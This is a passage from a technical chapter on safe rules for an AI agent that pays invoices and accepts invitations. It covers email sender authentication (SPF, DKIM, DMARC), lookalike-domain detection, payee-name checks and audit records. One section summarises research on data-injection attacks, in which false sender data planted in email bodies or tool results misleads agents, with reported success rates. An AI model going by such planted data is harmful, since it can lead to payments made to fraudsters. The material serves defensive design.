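An email has two sender addresses. Mail servers use the envelope address to deliver the message and report a failed delivery, and the recipient normally doesn't see it. Mail programs display the From address. Microsoft's *Create safe sender lists in EOP* gives the example of an airline that hires a travel agency to send its advertising, so that the envelope address belongs to the agency and the From address to the airline.

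The Sender Policy Framework (SPF) checks the envelope address. A domain's owner publishes a list of the servers that may send its mail. The list is in the domain name system (DNS), the public directory computers use to look up domains. The receiving server checks whether the server delivering the message is on the envelope domain's list. SPF ignores the From address, and Kucherawy (2019) notes in *Message Header Field for Indicating Message Authentication Status* that SPF doesn't validate any other property of the message itself.

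With DomainKeys Identified Mail (DKIM), the sending server signs parts of the message with a private key and names the signing domain. The receiving server fetches the matching public key from that domain's DNS records and checks the signature. A valid signature shows that the signer had the domain's private key and that nobody changed the signed parts in transit. However, the signing domain can differ from the domain in the From address.

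A forger who owns attacker.example can therefore pass both checks. They publish an SPF list that includes their own server, sign the message as attacker.example, and write Northfield's address in the From line.

### DMARC and alignment

DMARC (Domain-based Message Authentication, Reporting, and Conformance) connects these checks to the From address. Herr and Levine (2026), in *Domain-Based Message Authentication, Reporting, and Conformance (DMARC)*, set out the current standard, which replaced a 2015 version in May 2026. A message passes when:

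```
the From domain has published a DMARC record
AND (   SPF passed for a domain that aligns with the From domain
     OR a DKIM signature is valid for a domain that aligns with it )
```

Strict alignment requires the two domains to be identical. Relaxed alignment, the default, only requires them to belong to the same organisation's domain, so mail.northfield.example aligns with northfield.example. The domain's owner chooses which mode to use, and Herr and Levine report that nearly all owners find relaxed alignment sufficient.

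Suppose Northfield sends its November invoice from its own server. The server is on Northfield's SPF list, and the envelope address, the signature and the From address all use northfield.example, so the message passes DMARC. On the same day, the forger sends an invoice that passes SPF and DKIM for attacker.example, but neither result aligns with northfield.example, so DMARC fails. Software that looked only for "SPF pass" and "DKIM pass" would accept the forgery. The forger could put northfield.example in the envelope address too, but then SPF would fail, because the forger's server isn't on Northfield's list.

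DMARC validates the domain but not the part of the address before the @. If Northfield's mail system lets any employee write accounts@northfield.example in the From line, an attacker who takes over any mailbox at the firm can send an invoice that passes DMARC. In that case, listing one address instead of the whole domain gives no extra protection.

Relaxed alignment also carries a risk. Herr and Levine describe how an attacker who controls the DNS records of a subdomain, such as old.northfield.example, can publish an SPF list for it and send mail as accounts@northfield.example that passes DMARC. Northfield can prevent this by requiring strict alignment. If Northfield signs its mail with DKIM as northfield.example, the user's software can also block the attack by accepting only signatures from that exact domain.

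### Forwarding, mailing lists and billing services

Genuine mail can fail these checks. If the user's old address automatically forwards mail to a new one, the forwarding service's server makes the final delivery. SPF then usually fails, because that server isn't on Northfield's list. The forwarding service can avoid the failure by putting its own domain in the envelope address, but then the SPF result no longer aligns with Northfield's domain. A DKIM signature generally remains valid after forwarding, so the message can still pass DMARC.

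A mailing list often adds a footer or changes the subject line, which can break the signature. A message with a broken signature fails DMARC if the list leaves the From address unchanged. Herr and Levine report that mailing-list software works around this by rewriting the From line, for example from bob@example.com to bob=example.com@user.somelist.example. The rewritten message can pass DMARC for the list's domain, but it no longer matches Bob's saved address. Developers have tried for a decade to avoid this rewriting, but none of their methods is widely used.

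An outside billing service can cause the same problem. If it sends Northfield's invoices from its own servers, and Northfield hasn't set up SPF or DKIM for it, the results are the same as for a forgery:

| Message with Northfield's From address | SPF | DKIM | DMARC |
|---|---|---|---|
| Genuine, sent directly | Pass for Northfield | Pass for Northfield | Pass |
| Forged | Pass for the forger | Pass for the forger | Fail |
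| Genuine, forwarded automatically | Fail | Pass for Northfield | Pass |
| Genuine, altered by a mailing list | Pass for the list | Fail | Fail |
| Genuine, from a billing service that isn't set up | Pass for the service | Pass for the service | Fail |

Rule B should send all failures to the user, even those that are probably innocent. A failed check on a genuine invoice leads to one prompt, estimated earlier to cost 10 cents. An exception for forwarded or outsourced mail would avoid that prompt, but a forger could use the exception too.

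### Mail that fails can still reach the inbox

In a DMARC record, a domain's owner can ask receivers to treat mail that fails the check as suspicious, ask them to reject it, or express no preference. Receivers don't have to comply. Herr and Levine tell them not to reject a message solely because the domain's owner asked them to, since this would lose genuine mail sent through forwarders and mailing lists.

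A forged invoice may therefore fail DMARC and still appear in the mailbox that the agent reads, so Rule B needs to check the result itself and should accept only "pass". DMARC can also return "none" if the From domain has no DMARC record, or an error if, for example, a DNS server doesn't respond. DMARC may not run at all on messages that name several From domains, but the exact-match procedure already refers those to the user because they don't contain exactly one valid identifier.

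Veit and colleagues warn against assuming that protections such as DMARC are in place. Before saving Rule B, the user or the software should check whether Northfield's past invoices passed DMARC. If Northfield has no DMARC record, the user can ask it to publish one. Correctly sent invoices will pass even if the record requests no action against messages that fail.

### Safe-sender lists

Email administrators face a similar decision when they let a trusted sender skip spam filtering. Microsoft warns them never to use the sender's domain as the only condition, because an attacker could spoof the domain and get past the filter. Its example also requires the mail system to have recorded a DMARC result of "pass" or "bestguesspass". The latter means that the domain has no DMARC record but the message would have passed if it had one. For senders that don't use authentication, Microsoft recommends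 limiting the exception to as few server addresses as possible.

Microsoft ranks five ways of exempting senders, and puts the lists of allowed senders and domains in the anti-spam settings last. Mail from listed senders skips the spam, spoofing, SPF, DKIM and DMARC checks. Microsoft still quarantines malware and messages that it is highly confident are phishing, meaning attempts to trick people into giving up passwords or money. It recommends these lists only for temporary testing.

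Outlook users have a similar list. Microsoft's *Add recipients to the Safe Senders List in Outlook* explains that Outlook never treats mail from these senders as junk, whatever it contains, and that the list includes the user's contacts by default. Some other checks still apply, according to Microsoft's *Configure junk email settings on EXO mailboxes*. But a user who adds Northfield so that its invoices don't go missing also makes it easier for a forged invoice to reach the inbox. An agent that can add contacts without asking could exempt a stranger from the junk filter, even though adding a contact looks harmless.

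The software should therefore keep the list of people whose mail the user wants to receive separate from the list of people it may pay. Permission to pay an invoice is much bigger than permission to deliver it, so Rule B should require at least as much proof of who sent the message as Microsoft recommends for skipping a spam filter.

### Where the check has to run

The receiving mail server has to run the SPF check, because it can see which server delivered the message. The agent's software gets the message later. It could check the DKIM signature itself, since the signature travels with the message, but it's simpler to read the results that the server recorded. The server adds them to the top of the message in a field called Authentication-Results:

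```
Authentication-Results: mail.user.example;
    spf=pass smtp.mailfrom=northfield.example;
    dkim=pass header.d=northfield.example;
    dmarc=pass header.from=northfield.example
```

Here mail.user.example identifies the user's own mail system. A forger could write the same lines into a message before sending it. Kucherawy notes that the field's presence doesn't make its contents valid, and requires the receiving system to remove any incoming copy that names that system as its source.

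The software should use only the authentication results from the user's own mail system, and only if that system removes forged copies of them. It must not search the whole message for "dmarc=pass". It should also ignore results inside an attached email, because whoever attached the email could have changed them.

A calendar invitation handled under Rule A can name an organiser in the calendar data as well as a sender in the From line. DMARC evaluates only the From line, so the software should compare that address with the allowlist. If it compared the organiser instead, an attacker could send an invitation from their own authenticated address, name Northfield as the organiser, and match the allowlist.

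### When a model misreads the sender

The results also have to reach the rule without passing through the model. A mail tool typically gives the model the sender's address and the message body together as text, and the model can confuse them. *Agent Data Injection Attacks are Realistic Threats to AI Agents* (Choi, Kim and colleagues, 2026) tested whether an attacker could make a model mistake outside text, such as part of an email's body, for trusted data, such as the sender field. With data in JSON, a common format for tool results, the attacks succeeded 31.3% to 43.3% of the time across six models.

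These attacks give the model false information, such as the wrong sender, which it uses as it continues with the user's task. Defences against planted instructions offer less protection because the attacks don't need to include an instruction. In tests of the best available defences for agents, planted instructions succeeded at most 0.7% of the time, while false data succeeded up to 50.0% of the time. Choi and colleagues also demonstrated attacks on commercial agents, including one that made a coding agent mistake an outsider's comment for a project maintainer's. OpenAI, Google and Anthropic acknowledged the problems the researchers reported.

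The rates come from deliberate attacks by someone who knows the format of the agent's data, so they don't measure how often a model would misread ordinary mail. But an attacker can send more than one email. If each attempt had a 31.3% chance of success and the attempts were independent, the chance of at least one success in three attempts would be about 68%. Even a much lower rate would be too high for a payment rule.

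Ordinary code should therefore read the From address and the DMARC result in the mail system's own fields to decide whether Northfield sent the invoice.

There is still a gap, because the software needs to know which message to look up, and the model supplies that reference in its call. A stranger's email might lead the model to cite Northfield's genuine invoice from October. The software would find the right sender and a DMARC pass on the October message, and could then allow a November payment that Northfield never requested. The saved bank account ensures that the money would still go to Northfield, but Rule B should also refuse to use the same message twice. It needs two more conditions:

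```
AND   the user's mail system recorded a DMARC pass for northfield.example
AND   Rule B has attempted no earlier payment for this message
```

### Hijacked accounts

An attacker who gets the password to Northfield's accounts mailbox can send invoices through Northfield's server with Northfield's signature. These invoices pass SPF, DKIM, DMARC and the exact match, because none of these checks can detect who is using the mailbox. A lookalike domain can also pass authentication, since it belongs to the attacker, but the exact match rejects it.

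Business email compromise is fraud in which a criminal takes over or imitates a business email account, usually to redirect a payment. The FBI's *2025 IC3 Report* (2026) ranks it second among internet crimes by reported losses, after investment fraud. Adams and Reese's *FBI Releases 2025 Internet Crime Report* reports 24,768 complaints and $3.046 billion in losses for 2025, up from 21,442 complaints and $2.77 billion in 2024. The 2025 losses averaged about $123,000 per complaint. Most of the money went by wire transfer, according to CyberScoop.

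The FBI lists a single loss figure for business email compromise, without separating spoofed addresses, lookalike domains and hijacked mailboxes, so it can't show how much of this fraud sender authentication would prevent. The figure also leaves out unreported losses.

Rule B's limits on the bank account, amount and frequency still work when the attacker controls Northfield's mailbox. To steal the money paid on an invoice that meets all three limits, the attacker would also need to control Northfield's bank account or the user's saved payment details.

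The original Rule B had no condition on the bank account. Adding a DMARC check to it would have stopped spoofed invoices but not these. For a payment rule, requiring the saved bank account is the more important protection, because it limits where the money can go no matter who sent the invoice.

The average loss of $123,000 suggests that many criminals seek payments far larger than Rule B allows. A request of that size would produce a prompt, and a user who recognises Northfield's real address might approve the payment. The prompt should therefore show the condition that failed, such as "new bank account", more prominently than the sender's name. Blocking payments to unsaved accounts, as suggested earlier, would be safer still.

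Rule A has less protection against a hijacked mailbox. The attacker can send an invitation for a convenient hour, and the agent will accept it. Limits on length and frequency keep the wasted time small, but the invitation may contain a link to a fake meeting page that asks for the user's password. The user may trust the link more because the meeting is already on their calendar. Rule A should therefore not let the agent open links or join meetings, and the calendar entry could show that the agent accepted the invitation automatically.

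### Genuine senders that pass on hostile content

An account can also deliver hostile content without anyone hijacking it. Veit and colleagues describe file-sharing services that let people add a personal message to an invitation. An attacker shares a document and puts a harmful link in the message, and the service sends the invitation from its own address. The email comes from a genuine sender and can pass every authentication check, even though the attacker wrote part of it.

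This matters for Rule B if Northfield sends its invoices through a billing service that uses one address, such as invoices@billing.example, for all its customers. Saving that address would let anyone with an account at the service satisfy the sender condition. DMARC would correctly show that the service sent the message, but not which customer wrote the invoice. The user could ask Northfield to send invoices from its own domain. Otherwise the rule should also check a customer number that the service assigns and customers can't change, read from a field that the service fills in.

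Authentication also can't detect planted text in a client's document that Northfield forwards. Herr and Levine stress that a DMARC pass doesn't show whether a message is valuable or safe. The software should still treat everything in an authenticated email as untrusted. Passing the sender check can satisfy one condition of Rule A or B, but it shouldn't give the email's text any authority over the agent's other actions.

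### When to confirm through a second channel

For some requests, the user needs to confirm with Northfield outside email. An attacker who controls the mailbox can answer any reply, so neither the user nor the agent should confirm by email. The user should phone a number from an old bill or signed contract, since an attacker can put a false number in the new message.

A five-minute call costs $3 at the $36 an hour used earlier. If the call catches every fraud, it is worth making when the expected loss without it exceeds $3. For a $180 invoice, that means a chance of fraud above about 1.7%, or one in 60. A routine invoice that meets all of Rule B's conditions should be well below that. For a $5,000 invoice, the threshold is only 0.06%, or about one in 1,700.

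A change of bank details needs a call even when the next bill is small, because it affects every later payment. At $180 a month, a false account could receive $2,160 in a year. If the user wouldn't notice sooner, the call is worthwhile even if the chance of fraud is only one in 720. After the call, the user should enter the new account number in the rule's settings. The agent shouldn't copy it from the email, because the number there could be an attacker's and not the one Northfield confirmed.

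## Similarity checks and lookalike senders

An exact match rejects invoices from a lookalike such as northfie1d.example, but it also rejects Northfield's own invoices if the firm moves to northfieldbooks.example. A similarity check accepts any address close enough to a saved one, and whether this helps depends on how the software measures closeness.

### Ways to measure closeness

Edit distance, also called Levenshtein distance, is the smallest number of single-character replacements, insertions or deletions that turn one string into another. Replacing the digit 1 with the letter l turns northfie1d into northfield, so the two are one edit apart.

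Software finds the distance by filling in a table. Let D(i, j) be the distance between the first *i* characters of one name and the first *j* characters of the other. Turning *i* characters into nothing takes *i* deletions, so D(i, 0) = *i*, and similarly D(0, j) = *j*. Every other entry follows from its neighbours:

```
D(i, j) = the smallest of
            D(i-1, j) + 1       delete a character
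            D(i, j-1) + 1       insert a character
            D(i-1, j-1) + r     keep the character (r = 0) or replace it (r = 1)
```

The last entry is the distance between the full names. Swapping two neighbouring letters, as in northfeild, takes two edits. A variant called Damerau–Levenshtein distance counts such a swap as one.

Jaro–Winkler similarity runs from 0 to 1 and is common in software that matches people's names across records. Let *m* be the number of characters the two names share at roughly the same position, *t* half the number of shared characters that are out of order, and *k* the number of opening letters they have in common, up to four. For names *a* and *b*:

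```
J  = ( m/length(a) + m/length(b) + (m - t)/m ) / 3
JW = J + 0.1 × k × (1 - J)
```

Northfield and northfie1d share nine of their ten characters, all in order, so J is (0.9 + 0.9 + 1)/3, or about 0.93. They also start with the same four letters, which raises the final score to 0.96. The bonus for a shared beginning makes sense for surnames, but an attacker can get it by keeping the first four letters unchanged.

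Neither measure takes account of what the characters look like. Replacing the l in northfield with a q is one edit, and so is replacing it with a 1, but only the second is likely to fool anyone. Unicode Consortium's *Unicode Security Mechanisms* (2025) sets out a method for finding strings that look alike. It reduces each string to a "skeleton" and compares the skeletons:

```
1. Split accented characters into a letter and an accent
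2. Remove invisible characters
3. Replace each character with the standard one it resembles
4. Repeat step 1
```

The data for step 3 map the digit 1 to the letter l, so northfie1d and northfield have the same skeleton. The method also catches lookalike letters from other alphabets. The standard's example is "paypal" written with the Cyrillic letter а. According to paultendo's *A threat model for Unicode identifier spoofing*, the data cover 6,565 characters.

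The comparison gives a yes or no, not a score. The Unicode Consortium chose this simpler form because measuring how closely each pair of characters resemble each other would need more computation and better data. The simpler form produces some false matches. If one string matches a second and the second matches a third, the first and third must match too, even if they look less alike. paultendo's *confusable detection without nfkc* describes an implementation that omits the step replacing m with rn because it caused too many false matches. With that step, "modem" and "modern" have the same skeleton.

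Embedding similarity compares meaning. A model turns each piece of text into a list of numbers, called an embedding, and tends to give similar lists to texts that people use in similar ways. The usual score is the cosine of the angle between the lists:

```
similarity(u, v) = (u · v) / (length(u) × length(v))
```

The cosine similarity of the two-number lists (3, 4) and (4, 3) is 24/(5 × 5), or 0.96. Real embeddings have hundreds or thousands of numbers. "Northfield Bookkeeping" and "Northfield Accounts" would probably score high even though many of their letters differ, so embeddings could help to recognise a firm that has changed its name. But an attacker can register northfield-accounting.example, which is just as close in meaning, and an embedding contains no information about who owns a domain.

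A language model can also judge directly whether two addresses belong to the same sender. It can use the rest of the message, such as a note announcing that Northfield has moved to northfieldbooks.example, but an attacker can write the same note. Confirming the move requires evidence from outside the message, such as a phone call to the firm.

The letter-based measures give definite results for a few names:

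| Name | Possible holder | Edits from northfield | Jaro–Winkler | Same skeleton |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| northfie1d | Attacker | 1 | 0.96 | Yes |
| northfeild | Attacker | 2 | 0.98 | No |
| southfield | Unrelated firm | 2 | 0.87 | No |
| northern | Unrelated firm | 4 | 0.87 | No |
| northfieldbooks | Northfield, after its move | 5 | 0.93 | No |
| northfield-billing | Attacker | 8 | 0.91 | No |

Northfield's real new name scores worse than the forged northfie1d on every measure in the table, so any threshold loose enough to accept the new name would also accept the forgery.

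### Trusting every name within one edit

Suppose the user changes Rule B to tolerate one edit in the name before ".example". A domain name can use 37 characters: the 26 letters, the ten digits and the hyphen. The strings one edit from northfield are:

- **Replacements:** each of 10 letters can become any of 36 other characters, which gives 360 strings.
- **Insertions:** there are 11 places to insert one of 37 characters, which gives 407. Ten of these are duplicates, because adding a second n before the first n gives the same string as adding it after, and likewise for the other nine letters. That leaves 397.
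- **Deletions:** removing one letter gives 10 strings.

There are 767 strings one edit away from Northfield's name. Four begin or end with a hyphen, which domain names can't do, so 763 remain. The rule used to accept only the name Northfield owns. It now also accepts these 763, and anyone can register the ones that are free. Counting a swap of two adjacent letters as one edit adds nine more.

If a domain costs $10 a year, Northfield would have to pay $7,630 a year to register all of these names and be safe. An attacker needs only one, which would cost $10 and could bring in up to $2,400 a year under the original Rule B. The saved bank account in the revised rule would stop the theft, but the one-edit tolerance would still weaken the sender check without benefiting the user.

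One-edit tolerance has no benefit here because Northfield's mail program doesn't misspell its own address. People make typing errors when they enter a name by hand, but software fills in the From line the same way every time. If Northfield changes its domain, it will probably choose a name that people can tell apart from the old one, such as northfieldbooks, which one-edit tolerance won't accept. An attacker wants a name that people will mistake for the old one. An unlisted address one edit from a saved one is therefore more likely to be an attack than an honest variation, so the similarity is a reason to withhold permission.

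Raising the threshold makes this worse. Allowing two edits adds more than 140,000 strings from double replacements and double insertions alone. One of them is southfield, and southfield.example might belong to a real firm that sends invoices. Accepting northfieldbooks requires a threshold of five, which also lets in northern.example. Accepting northfield-billing requires a threshold of eight, which also lets in ford.example, since "ford" is seven edits from "northfield".

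Short names have the same problem at a threshold of one. The names of the American parcel company UPS and the United States Postal Service, USPS, differ by one inserted letter, so a rule for either would accept the other.

A percentage threshold may be less strict than it sounds. The address accounts@northfield.example has 27 characters, and accounts@southfield.example differs from it by two, so they are about 93% alike. If a rule requires only 90% similarity to Northfield's whole address, the agent would also pay Southfield's invoices. Most of the score comes from the matching parts of the address, but an attacker can copy everything except the exact domain.

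A check that compares only the part of the domain before the ending has the opposite fault, because it finds zero edits between northfield.test and northfield.example, which different people can own. Veit and colleagues list changes to the ending and to other parts of the address among the ways attackers disguise a sender. For example, an attacker can put a trusted-looking domain before the @ sign, as in northfield.example@attacker.example. They point out that some people read only the beginning of an address. Edit distance between the two domains would show no resemblance, since "attacker" is nothing like "northfield".

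### Permission from exact matches, warnings from similarity

Similarity checks are much more useful for warning the user. Their mistakes then cost far less, as a comparison of the two roles shows:

| What happens | If similarity grants permission | If similarity only warns |
|---|---|---|
| A lookalike scores as close | The agent pays the attacker | The user gets a prompt with a warning |
| A lookalike scores as distant | The user gets a prompt | The user gets a prompt |
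| An unrelated firm scores as close | The agent may pay the wrong firm | The user gets an unnecessary warning |
| Northfield's new address scores as distant | The user gets a prompt | The user gets a prompt |

The table assumes that the rule's other conditions hold. If similarity grants permission, an attacker who gets a high score gets paid. If it only triggers a warning, the attacker needs a low score to avoid it, and the invoice still goes to the user. A name different enough to avoid the warning is also easier for the user to recognise as unfamiliar, though northfield-billing shows that this isn't guaranteed.

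The sender check for Rule B could therefore run in this order:

```
1. If the address is on the allowlist exactly, check the rule's other conditions
2. If its domain has the same skeleton as a different listed domain, block the payment
3. If its domain is within two edits of a listed one, ask with a warning
4. If a listed name appears anywhere else in the sender line, ask with a warning
5. Otherwise, ask as usual
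```

Blocking makes sense in step 2 because there are few innocent reasons for a new supplier's domain to look the same as Northfield's. If the supplier is legitimate, the user can still add its exact domain to the list after checking with the firm. Step 3 only warns because two edits are weaker evidence, and refusing every invoice from Southfield would be unreasonable.

Step 4 catches northfield-billing.example, which steps 2 and 3 miss. It also catches northfieldbooks.example, where a warning is appropriate because the software can't tell whether Northfield has really moved to that domain. If a firm's name is a common word, such as Field, step 4 would produce many false alarms, and the user might turn it off.

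The warning has to show how the address differs from the saved one. "This sender may be suspicious" gives a busy person little to act on. A better message would be "This is not Northfield's saved address. The ninth character is the digit 1, not the letter l." The warning shouldn't include the question "Did you mean Northfield?" or an offer to merge the two addresses, since either would encourage the user to trust the attacker.

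The exact match should use the lower-cased address, but a similarity check that warns people should start from the address as it appears on the screen. A capital I looks like a small l in many fonts, so an attacker who owns northfieid.example can write it as northfieId.example to imitate northfield.example. Lower-casing turns the capital I into an ordinary i, which removes the resemblance. For this reason, the implementation that paultendo describes computes the skeleton before lower-casing.

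Domain names store non-Latin letters in a coded form that begins with "xn--". A domain containing the Cyrillic о may look identical to northfield on the screen but very different in storage, so a similarity check has to decode the name first. Skeletons also change between versions of Unicode, and the Unicode Consortium says that software must recompute stored skeletons after an update. This means that a check repeated later may give a different result.

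### Low-stakes actions and senders with many addresses

The case for granting permission by similarity is strongest when a mistake would do little harm and the senders are hard to list. Suppose the user wants the agent to move notices from their choir into a "Choir" folder. Volunteers send the notices from their own addresses, and the volunteers change every few months. An allowlist would keep going out of date, and the only domains the addresses share belong to public mail providers. An embedding or a language model could recognise the notices by their content.

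Moving a misfiled message to the right place takes about ten seconds, the same as answering a prompt. At the earlier estimate of 10 cents for each, *L* equals *c*. Even with an attentive reviewer, filing without asking is therefore cheaper unless every decision would be wrong, and no allowlist could reduce the cost much further.

However, the folder can make a message look more trustworthy. If the agent files a lookalike's invoice among Northfield's real ones, the user may later pay it because it is in that folder. Another rule might even treat everything in the folder as coming from Northfield, and a low-stakes filing decision would then determine whether the invoice is paid. Similarity is a reasonable basis for filing only if the user can easily undo the filing, the filing sends nothing to anyone, and neither people nor other rules treat the result as proof of who the sender is.

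Rule A is less suitable, although its mistakes also do fairly little harm. An attacker with a lookalike domain can send as many invitations as they like, and each acceptance confirms that someone uses the address and is free at that hour. Northfield sends only a few invitations a year. Even if half of them came from new addresses, a similarity check would spare the user only one or two prompts a year.

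Having many addresses doesn't justify similarity matching either. An airline may send confirmations from dozens of addresses, but if they all use the airline's own domain, one exact domain entry covers them. A firm with five domains needs five entries, which someone can copy once from a list the firm has confirmed. Similarity matching saves substantial work only for groups with no fixed set of identifiers, like the choir, and these are also the groups an impostor can join most easily.

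Similarity can still help build the list. If mail from northfieldbooks.example mentions Northfield's customer number and resembles earlier invoices, the software could show it to the user as a possible change of address. After the user has confirmed the change with the firm by phone, the software would save the new address as an exact entry. The similarity check would help the user find the change but would not authorise any payment.

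### Mail filters that flag near-copies

Cloudflare's *Trusted domains* describes an email filter, Area 1, that marks a message as a spoof if the sender's domain is spelled similarly to the customer's own. The filter also treats recently created domains as malicious or suspicious, which helps because attackers may start using a lookalike domain within days of creating it.

To exempt domains from either check, a customer must add an entry to a list. Cloudflare gives the example of a company that has registered several lookalikes of its own name to keep them from other people. An entry can also be a pattern that covers many domains, but a loose pattern could exempt an attacker's domain too. OAuth's designers required exact addresses because of the same weakness.

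The filter as described compares senders with the customer's domain, so it would catch someone pretending to work at the user's company. It wouldn't necessarily catch northfie1d.example, which imitates a supplier. An agent's software can also check for imitated suppliers by comparing each sender with every entry on the payment allowlist.

### Europe's payee-name check

Since October 9, 2025, banks and other payment providers in the euro area have had to check how closely the payee's name matches the account number before the payer authorises a transfer. They can't charge extra for this check, according to Banco de España's *New Verification of Payee service launches for free on 9 October 2025* (2025).

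EBA's *A match made in heaven?* (2025), a note by practitioners at the Euro Banking Association, an industry group, sets out the steps. The payer enters a name and an account number. The payer's bank sends both to the payee's bank, which compares the name with its own records and returns one of four results:

| Result | What the payer learns |
|---|---|
| Match | The name fits the account |
| Close match | The name of the actual account holder |
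| No match | The money may go to someone other than the named payee |
| Check not possible | The same warning as for "no match" |

A close match therefore shows the payer the real name on the account so they can check it, but doesn't approve the payment. None of the four results blocks the transfer either, according to The Paypers' *Verification of Payee readiness by country* (2026).

Name checks need some tolerance because people type names by hand and companies use several versions of their own. EBA gives the example of "ABC Ltd" and "ABC Limited". These are four edits apart, while northfie1d is only one edit from northfield, so here too a legitimate difference can be larger than a fraudulent one. A bank that relied on edit distance alone would make poor decisions, so banks also need rules for abbreviations, titles and accents.

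EBA explains that each payee's bank chooses its own matching criteria and takes responsibility for the answer, so the same spelling difference can be a match at one bank and a close match at another. Some payment forms also cut off long names, which can cause a mismatch even when the payer typed the name correctly. The practitioners expected that customers who often see harmless mismatches might start to ignore the warnings, which would be a form of approval fatigue.

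The system is now widely used. The Paypers reports that 2,724 of the 2,806 providers on the scheme's register were answering checks in October 2026. The register doesn't show how often names match. The service run by Latvia's central bank processed 57.4 million requests between October 2025 and the end of February 2026, according to Latvijas Banka's *Results from the first months of the Instant Verification Service*.

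In a survey for the bank in February 2026, 68% of Latvia's population had noticed the check. Half of those, or about a third of the population, said it or a similar service had helped prevent an incorrect transfer. This is encouraging, but it is self-reported, and an incorrect transfer can be a typing error, so the survey doesn't show how much fraud the check stopped. Latvijas Banka's *Digital euro project* counts 29.9 million of the 34.8 million requests in 2025 as "successful", but doesn't specify whether that means the names matched.

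The main danger is that an agent receives a "close match" warning in place of the user and authorises the transfer anyway, so the user never sees the other name. The Paypers reports that the user may also have no claim to recover misdirected money if the transfer went ahead despite a warning. Rule B should let the agent pay without asking only if the result is "match", and require it to show the user any other result. If an abbreviation on Northfield's invoices causes a close match, the user can confirm the name with the firm once and save it exactly as the bank holds it.

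A match can also be misleading. The check should catch a forger who keeps Northfield's name on the invoice and replaces the account number. But if the forger opens an account under the name "Northfield Books" and puts that name on the invoice, the names will match and the money will still go to the wrong firm. The saved account number in Rule B protects against this because it doesn't depend on the name.

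### False alarms when attacks are rare

Even an accurate similarity check produces mostly false alarms if it runs on all incoming mail. Suppose one message in 10,000 comes from a lookalike, and a check catches 95% of lookalikes and wrongly flags 1% of other messages. For every 10,000 messages:

```
lookalikes flagged        1 × 0.95     =    0.95
other messages flagged    9,999 × 0.01 =   99.99
share of flags correct    0.95 / 100.94 =  0.94%
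```

The check shows about 106 warnings for each lookalike it catches. If each warning interrupts the user for ten seconds, the cost is about $10.60 per lookalike. That would be worth paying to stop a $180 theft if the user read the 106th warning as carefully as the first, but someone who has seen a hundred false warnings in a row will probably dismiss the real one.

A much larger share of the warnings is correct when the check runs only on messages that would prompt the user anyway. Suppose 51 of the 10,000 messages request a payment and come from addresses that aren't on the allowlist, and one of these is the lookalike. The user already has to look at all 51, so the check adds no prompts. With the same error rates, it wrongly flags 0.5 messages and catches 0.95 lookalikes on average, so about two-thirds of its warnings are correct. A false alarm takes the user only a few extra seconds to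 read a line of text.

Missing a lookalike adds little risk if the user still gets the ordinary prompt and doesn't take the absence of a warning as a sign of safety. Software shouldn't put a green tick on an unlisted sender just because its name doesn't resemble any on the list.

The 95% and 1% in this example are assumptions, and a single catch rate can be misleading for any similarity check. A check that flags everything within one edit catches every one-letter change but misses northfield-billing. Its measured catch rate depends on how many of each kind of lookalike the test contains, and an attacker who knows the threshold will use the kind it misses. The argument for using similarity only in warnings doesn't depend on the exact rates, because a lookalike that the check misses still can't trigger a payment.

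### Similarity between actions

A rule has to recognise the action as well as the sender, and matching by similarity can misidentify either. Yan built a program that assigns each of an agent's tools to categories such as reading, sending, deleting or spending, so that one rule can cover tools from many services. Three people independently labelled 120 tools, chosen to include ambiguous and high-stakes ones, from their names, descriptions and input formats.

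Yan tested four automatic labeling methods against labels people had agreed on. The first used embeddings to find the most similar other tool in the set and copied its labels. The second looked for words such as "delete", and the third sorted tools into broad levels of access. The fourth gave a language model the label definitions and asked it to choose. Because a tool can have several labels, the results show how often each method got the main label right and how often it got the full set of labels right.

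| Method | Main label correct | All labels correct |
|---|---|---|
| Most similar tool | 45.8% | 43.3% |
| Broad access levels | 75.8% | 16.7% |
| Keywords | 78.3% | 43.3% |
| Language model | 90.0% | 72.5% |

Copying the main label from the most similar tool did far worse than looking for keywords, probably because two tools can have nearly the same description but opposite effects. "Retrieve a message from the user's mailbox" and "Remove a message from the user's mailbox" differ by one word, but a user might allow the first and forbid the second. The method also had only 119 other tools to copy from, so it might do better with a larger collection.

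The language model was the best of the four, but it wasn't consistent. Yan had it label ten difficult tools and ten clear ones ten times each. The clear tools got the same labels every time, but five of the difficult ones got different action labels across runs. The same rule could therefore allow a call to such a tool one day and block it another.

Yan also simulated rules that forbid a whole category. Because of the model's labelling mistakes, the rules let through 14% of the tools they should have blocked and blocked 4% of those they should have allowed. Sending the model's uncertain answers to the user cut wrongly allowed tools to 11% but raised wrongly blocked tools to 7%. Many mistakes remained because the model had made them with high confidence. Yan concludes that the labelling isn't reliable enough to be a security boundary on its own.

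These errors occurred with ordinary tools, and Yan didn't test deliberately disguised ones. A dishonest developer could write a description that resembles a harmless tool's, much as an attacker chooses a domain that resembles Northfield's. Rule B should therefore name the exact tool, `pay_invoice`, and the exact service that provides it. If the service later adds a tool called `pay_invoices`, software can use a model's label to tell the user what the new tool seems to do, but the agent should ask before using it.

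## Auditing automatic actions

Rule B pays Northfield without showing the user anything first, so any check on a payment has to come afterwards, from the audit record. The user, or a company's administrator, will want to know why a payment ran, who could have triggered it, and what has changed since the last review. The answers depend on how the rule recognises a sender:

| | Exact match | Similarity check |
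|---|---|---|
| Why did the payment run? | The sender's address equals a saved one | The message scored above a threshold |
| Who could have triggered it? | Anyone who can send authenticated mail from the saved address | Anyone who can write a message that scores high enough |
| What has changed? | Edits to the rule or the allowlist | Those edits, plus any change to the model or its examples |

An explanation the model writes afterwards can't replace a record, because it is new text and may not describe how the decision was made. Li and colleagues similarly object to automated review because a model's approvals are opaque and can vary between runs, which makes them hard to audit.

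### Two records of one payment

Suppose Northfield's $180 invoice arrives on November 2, 2026, and Rule B pays it. The rule is now in its third version, which includes the saved bank account and the DMARC check. The software could store this:

```
Time               2026-11-02 09:14:07 UTC
Decision           allow
Rule               Rule B, version 3
Call               pay_invoice, 180.00 USD, Northfield's saved account
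Message            no. 48213 in the mailbox
From address       accounts@northfield.example
Matching entry     accounts@northfield.example
DMARC result       pass for northfield.example
Earlier attempts   0 this month, 0 in 14 days, 0 for this message
Outcome            sent, bank reference 550172
```

Anyone can check the sender condition by comparing two lines in the record. The record should also note where each value came from. The amount comes from the model's call, while the address and the DMARC result come from the mail system. If the software had copied the sender from the model's account of the message, an auditor would have no independent evidence of who sent it.

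Now suppose Rule B used an embedding model to recognise Northfield. The model compares the invoice with twelve earlier ones, and the rule requires an average score of at least 0.90. In place of the matching entry, the record would need:

```
Score              0.94
Threshold          0.90
Model              example-embed, version 2.1
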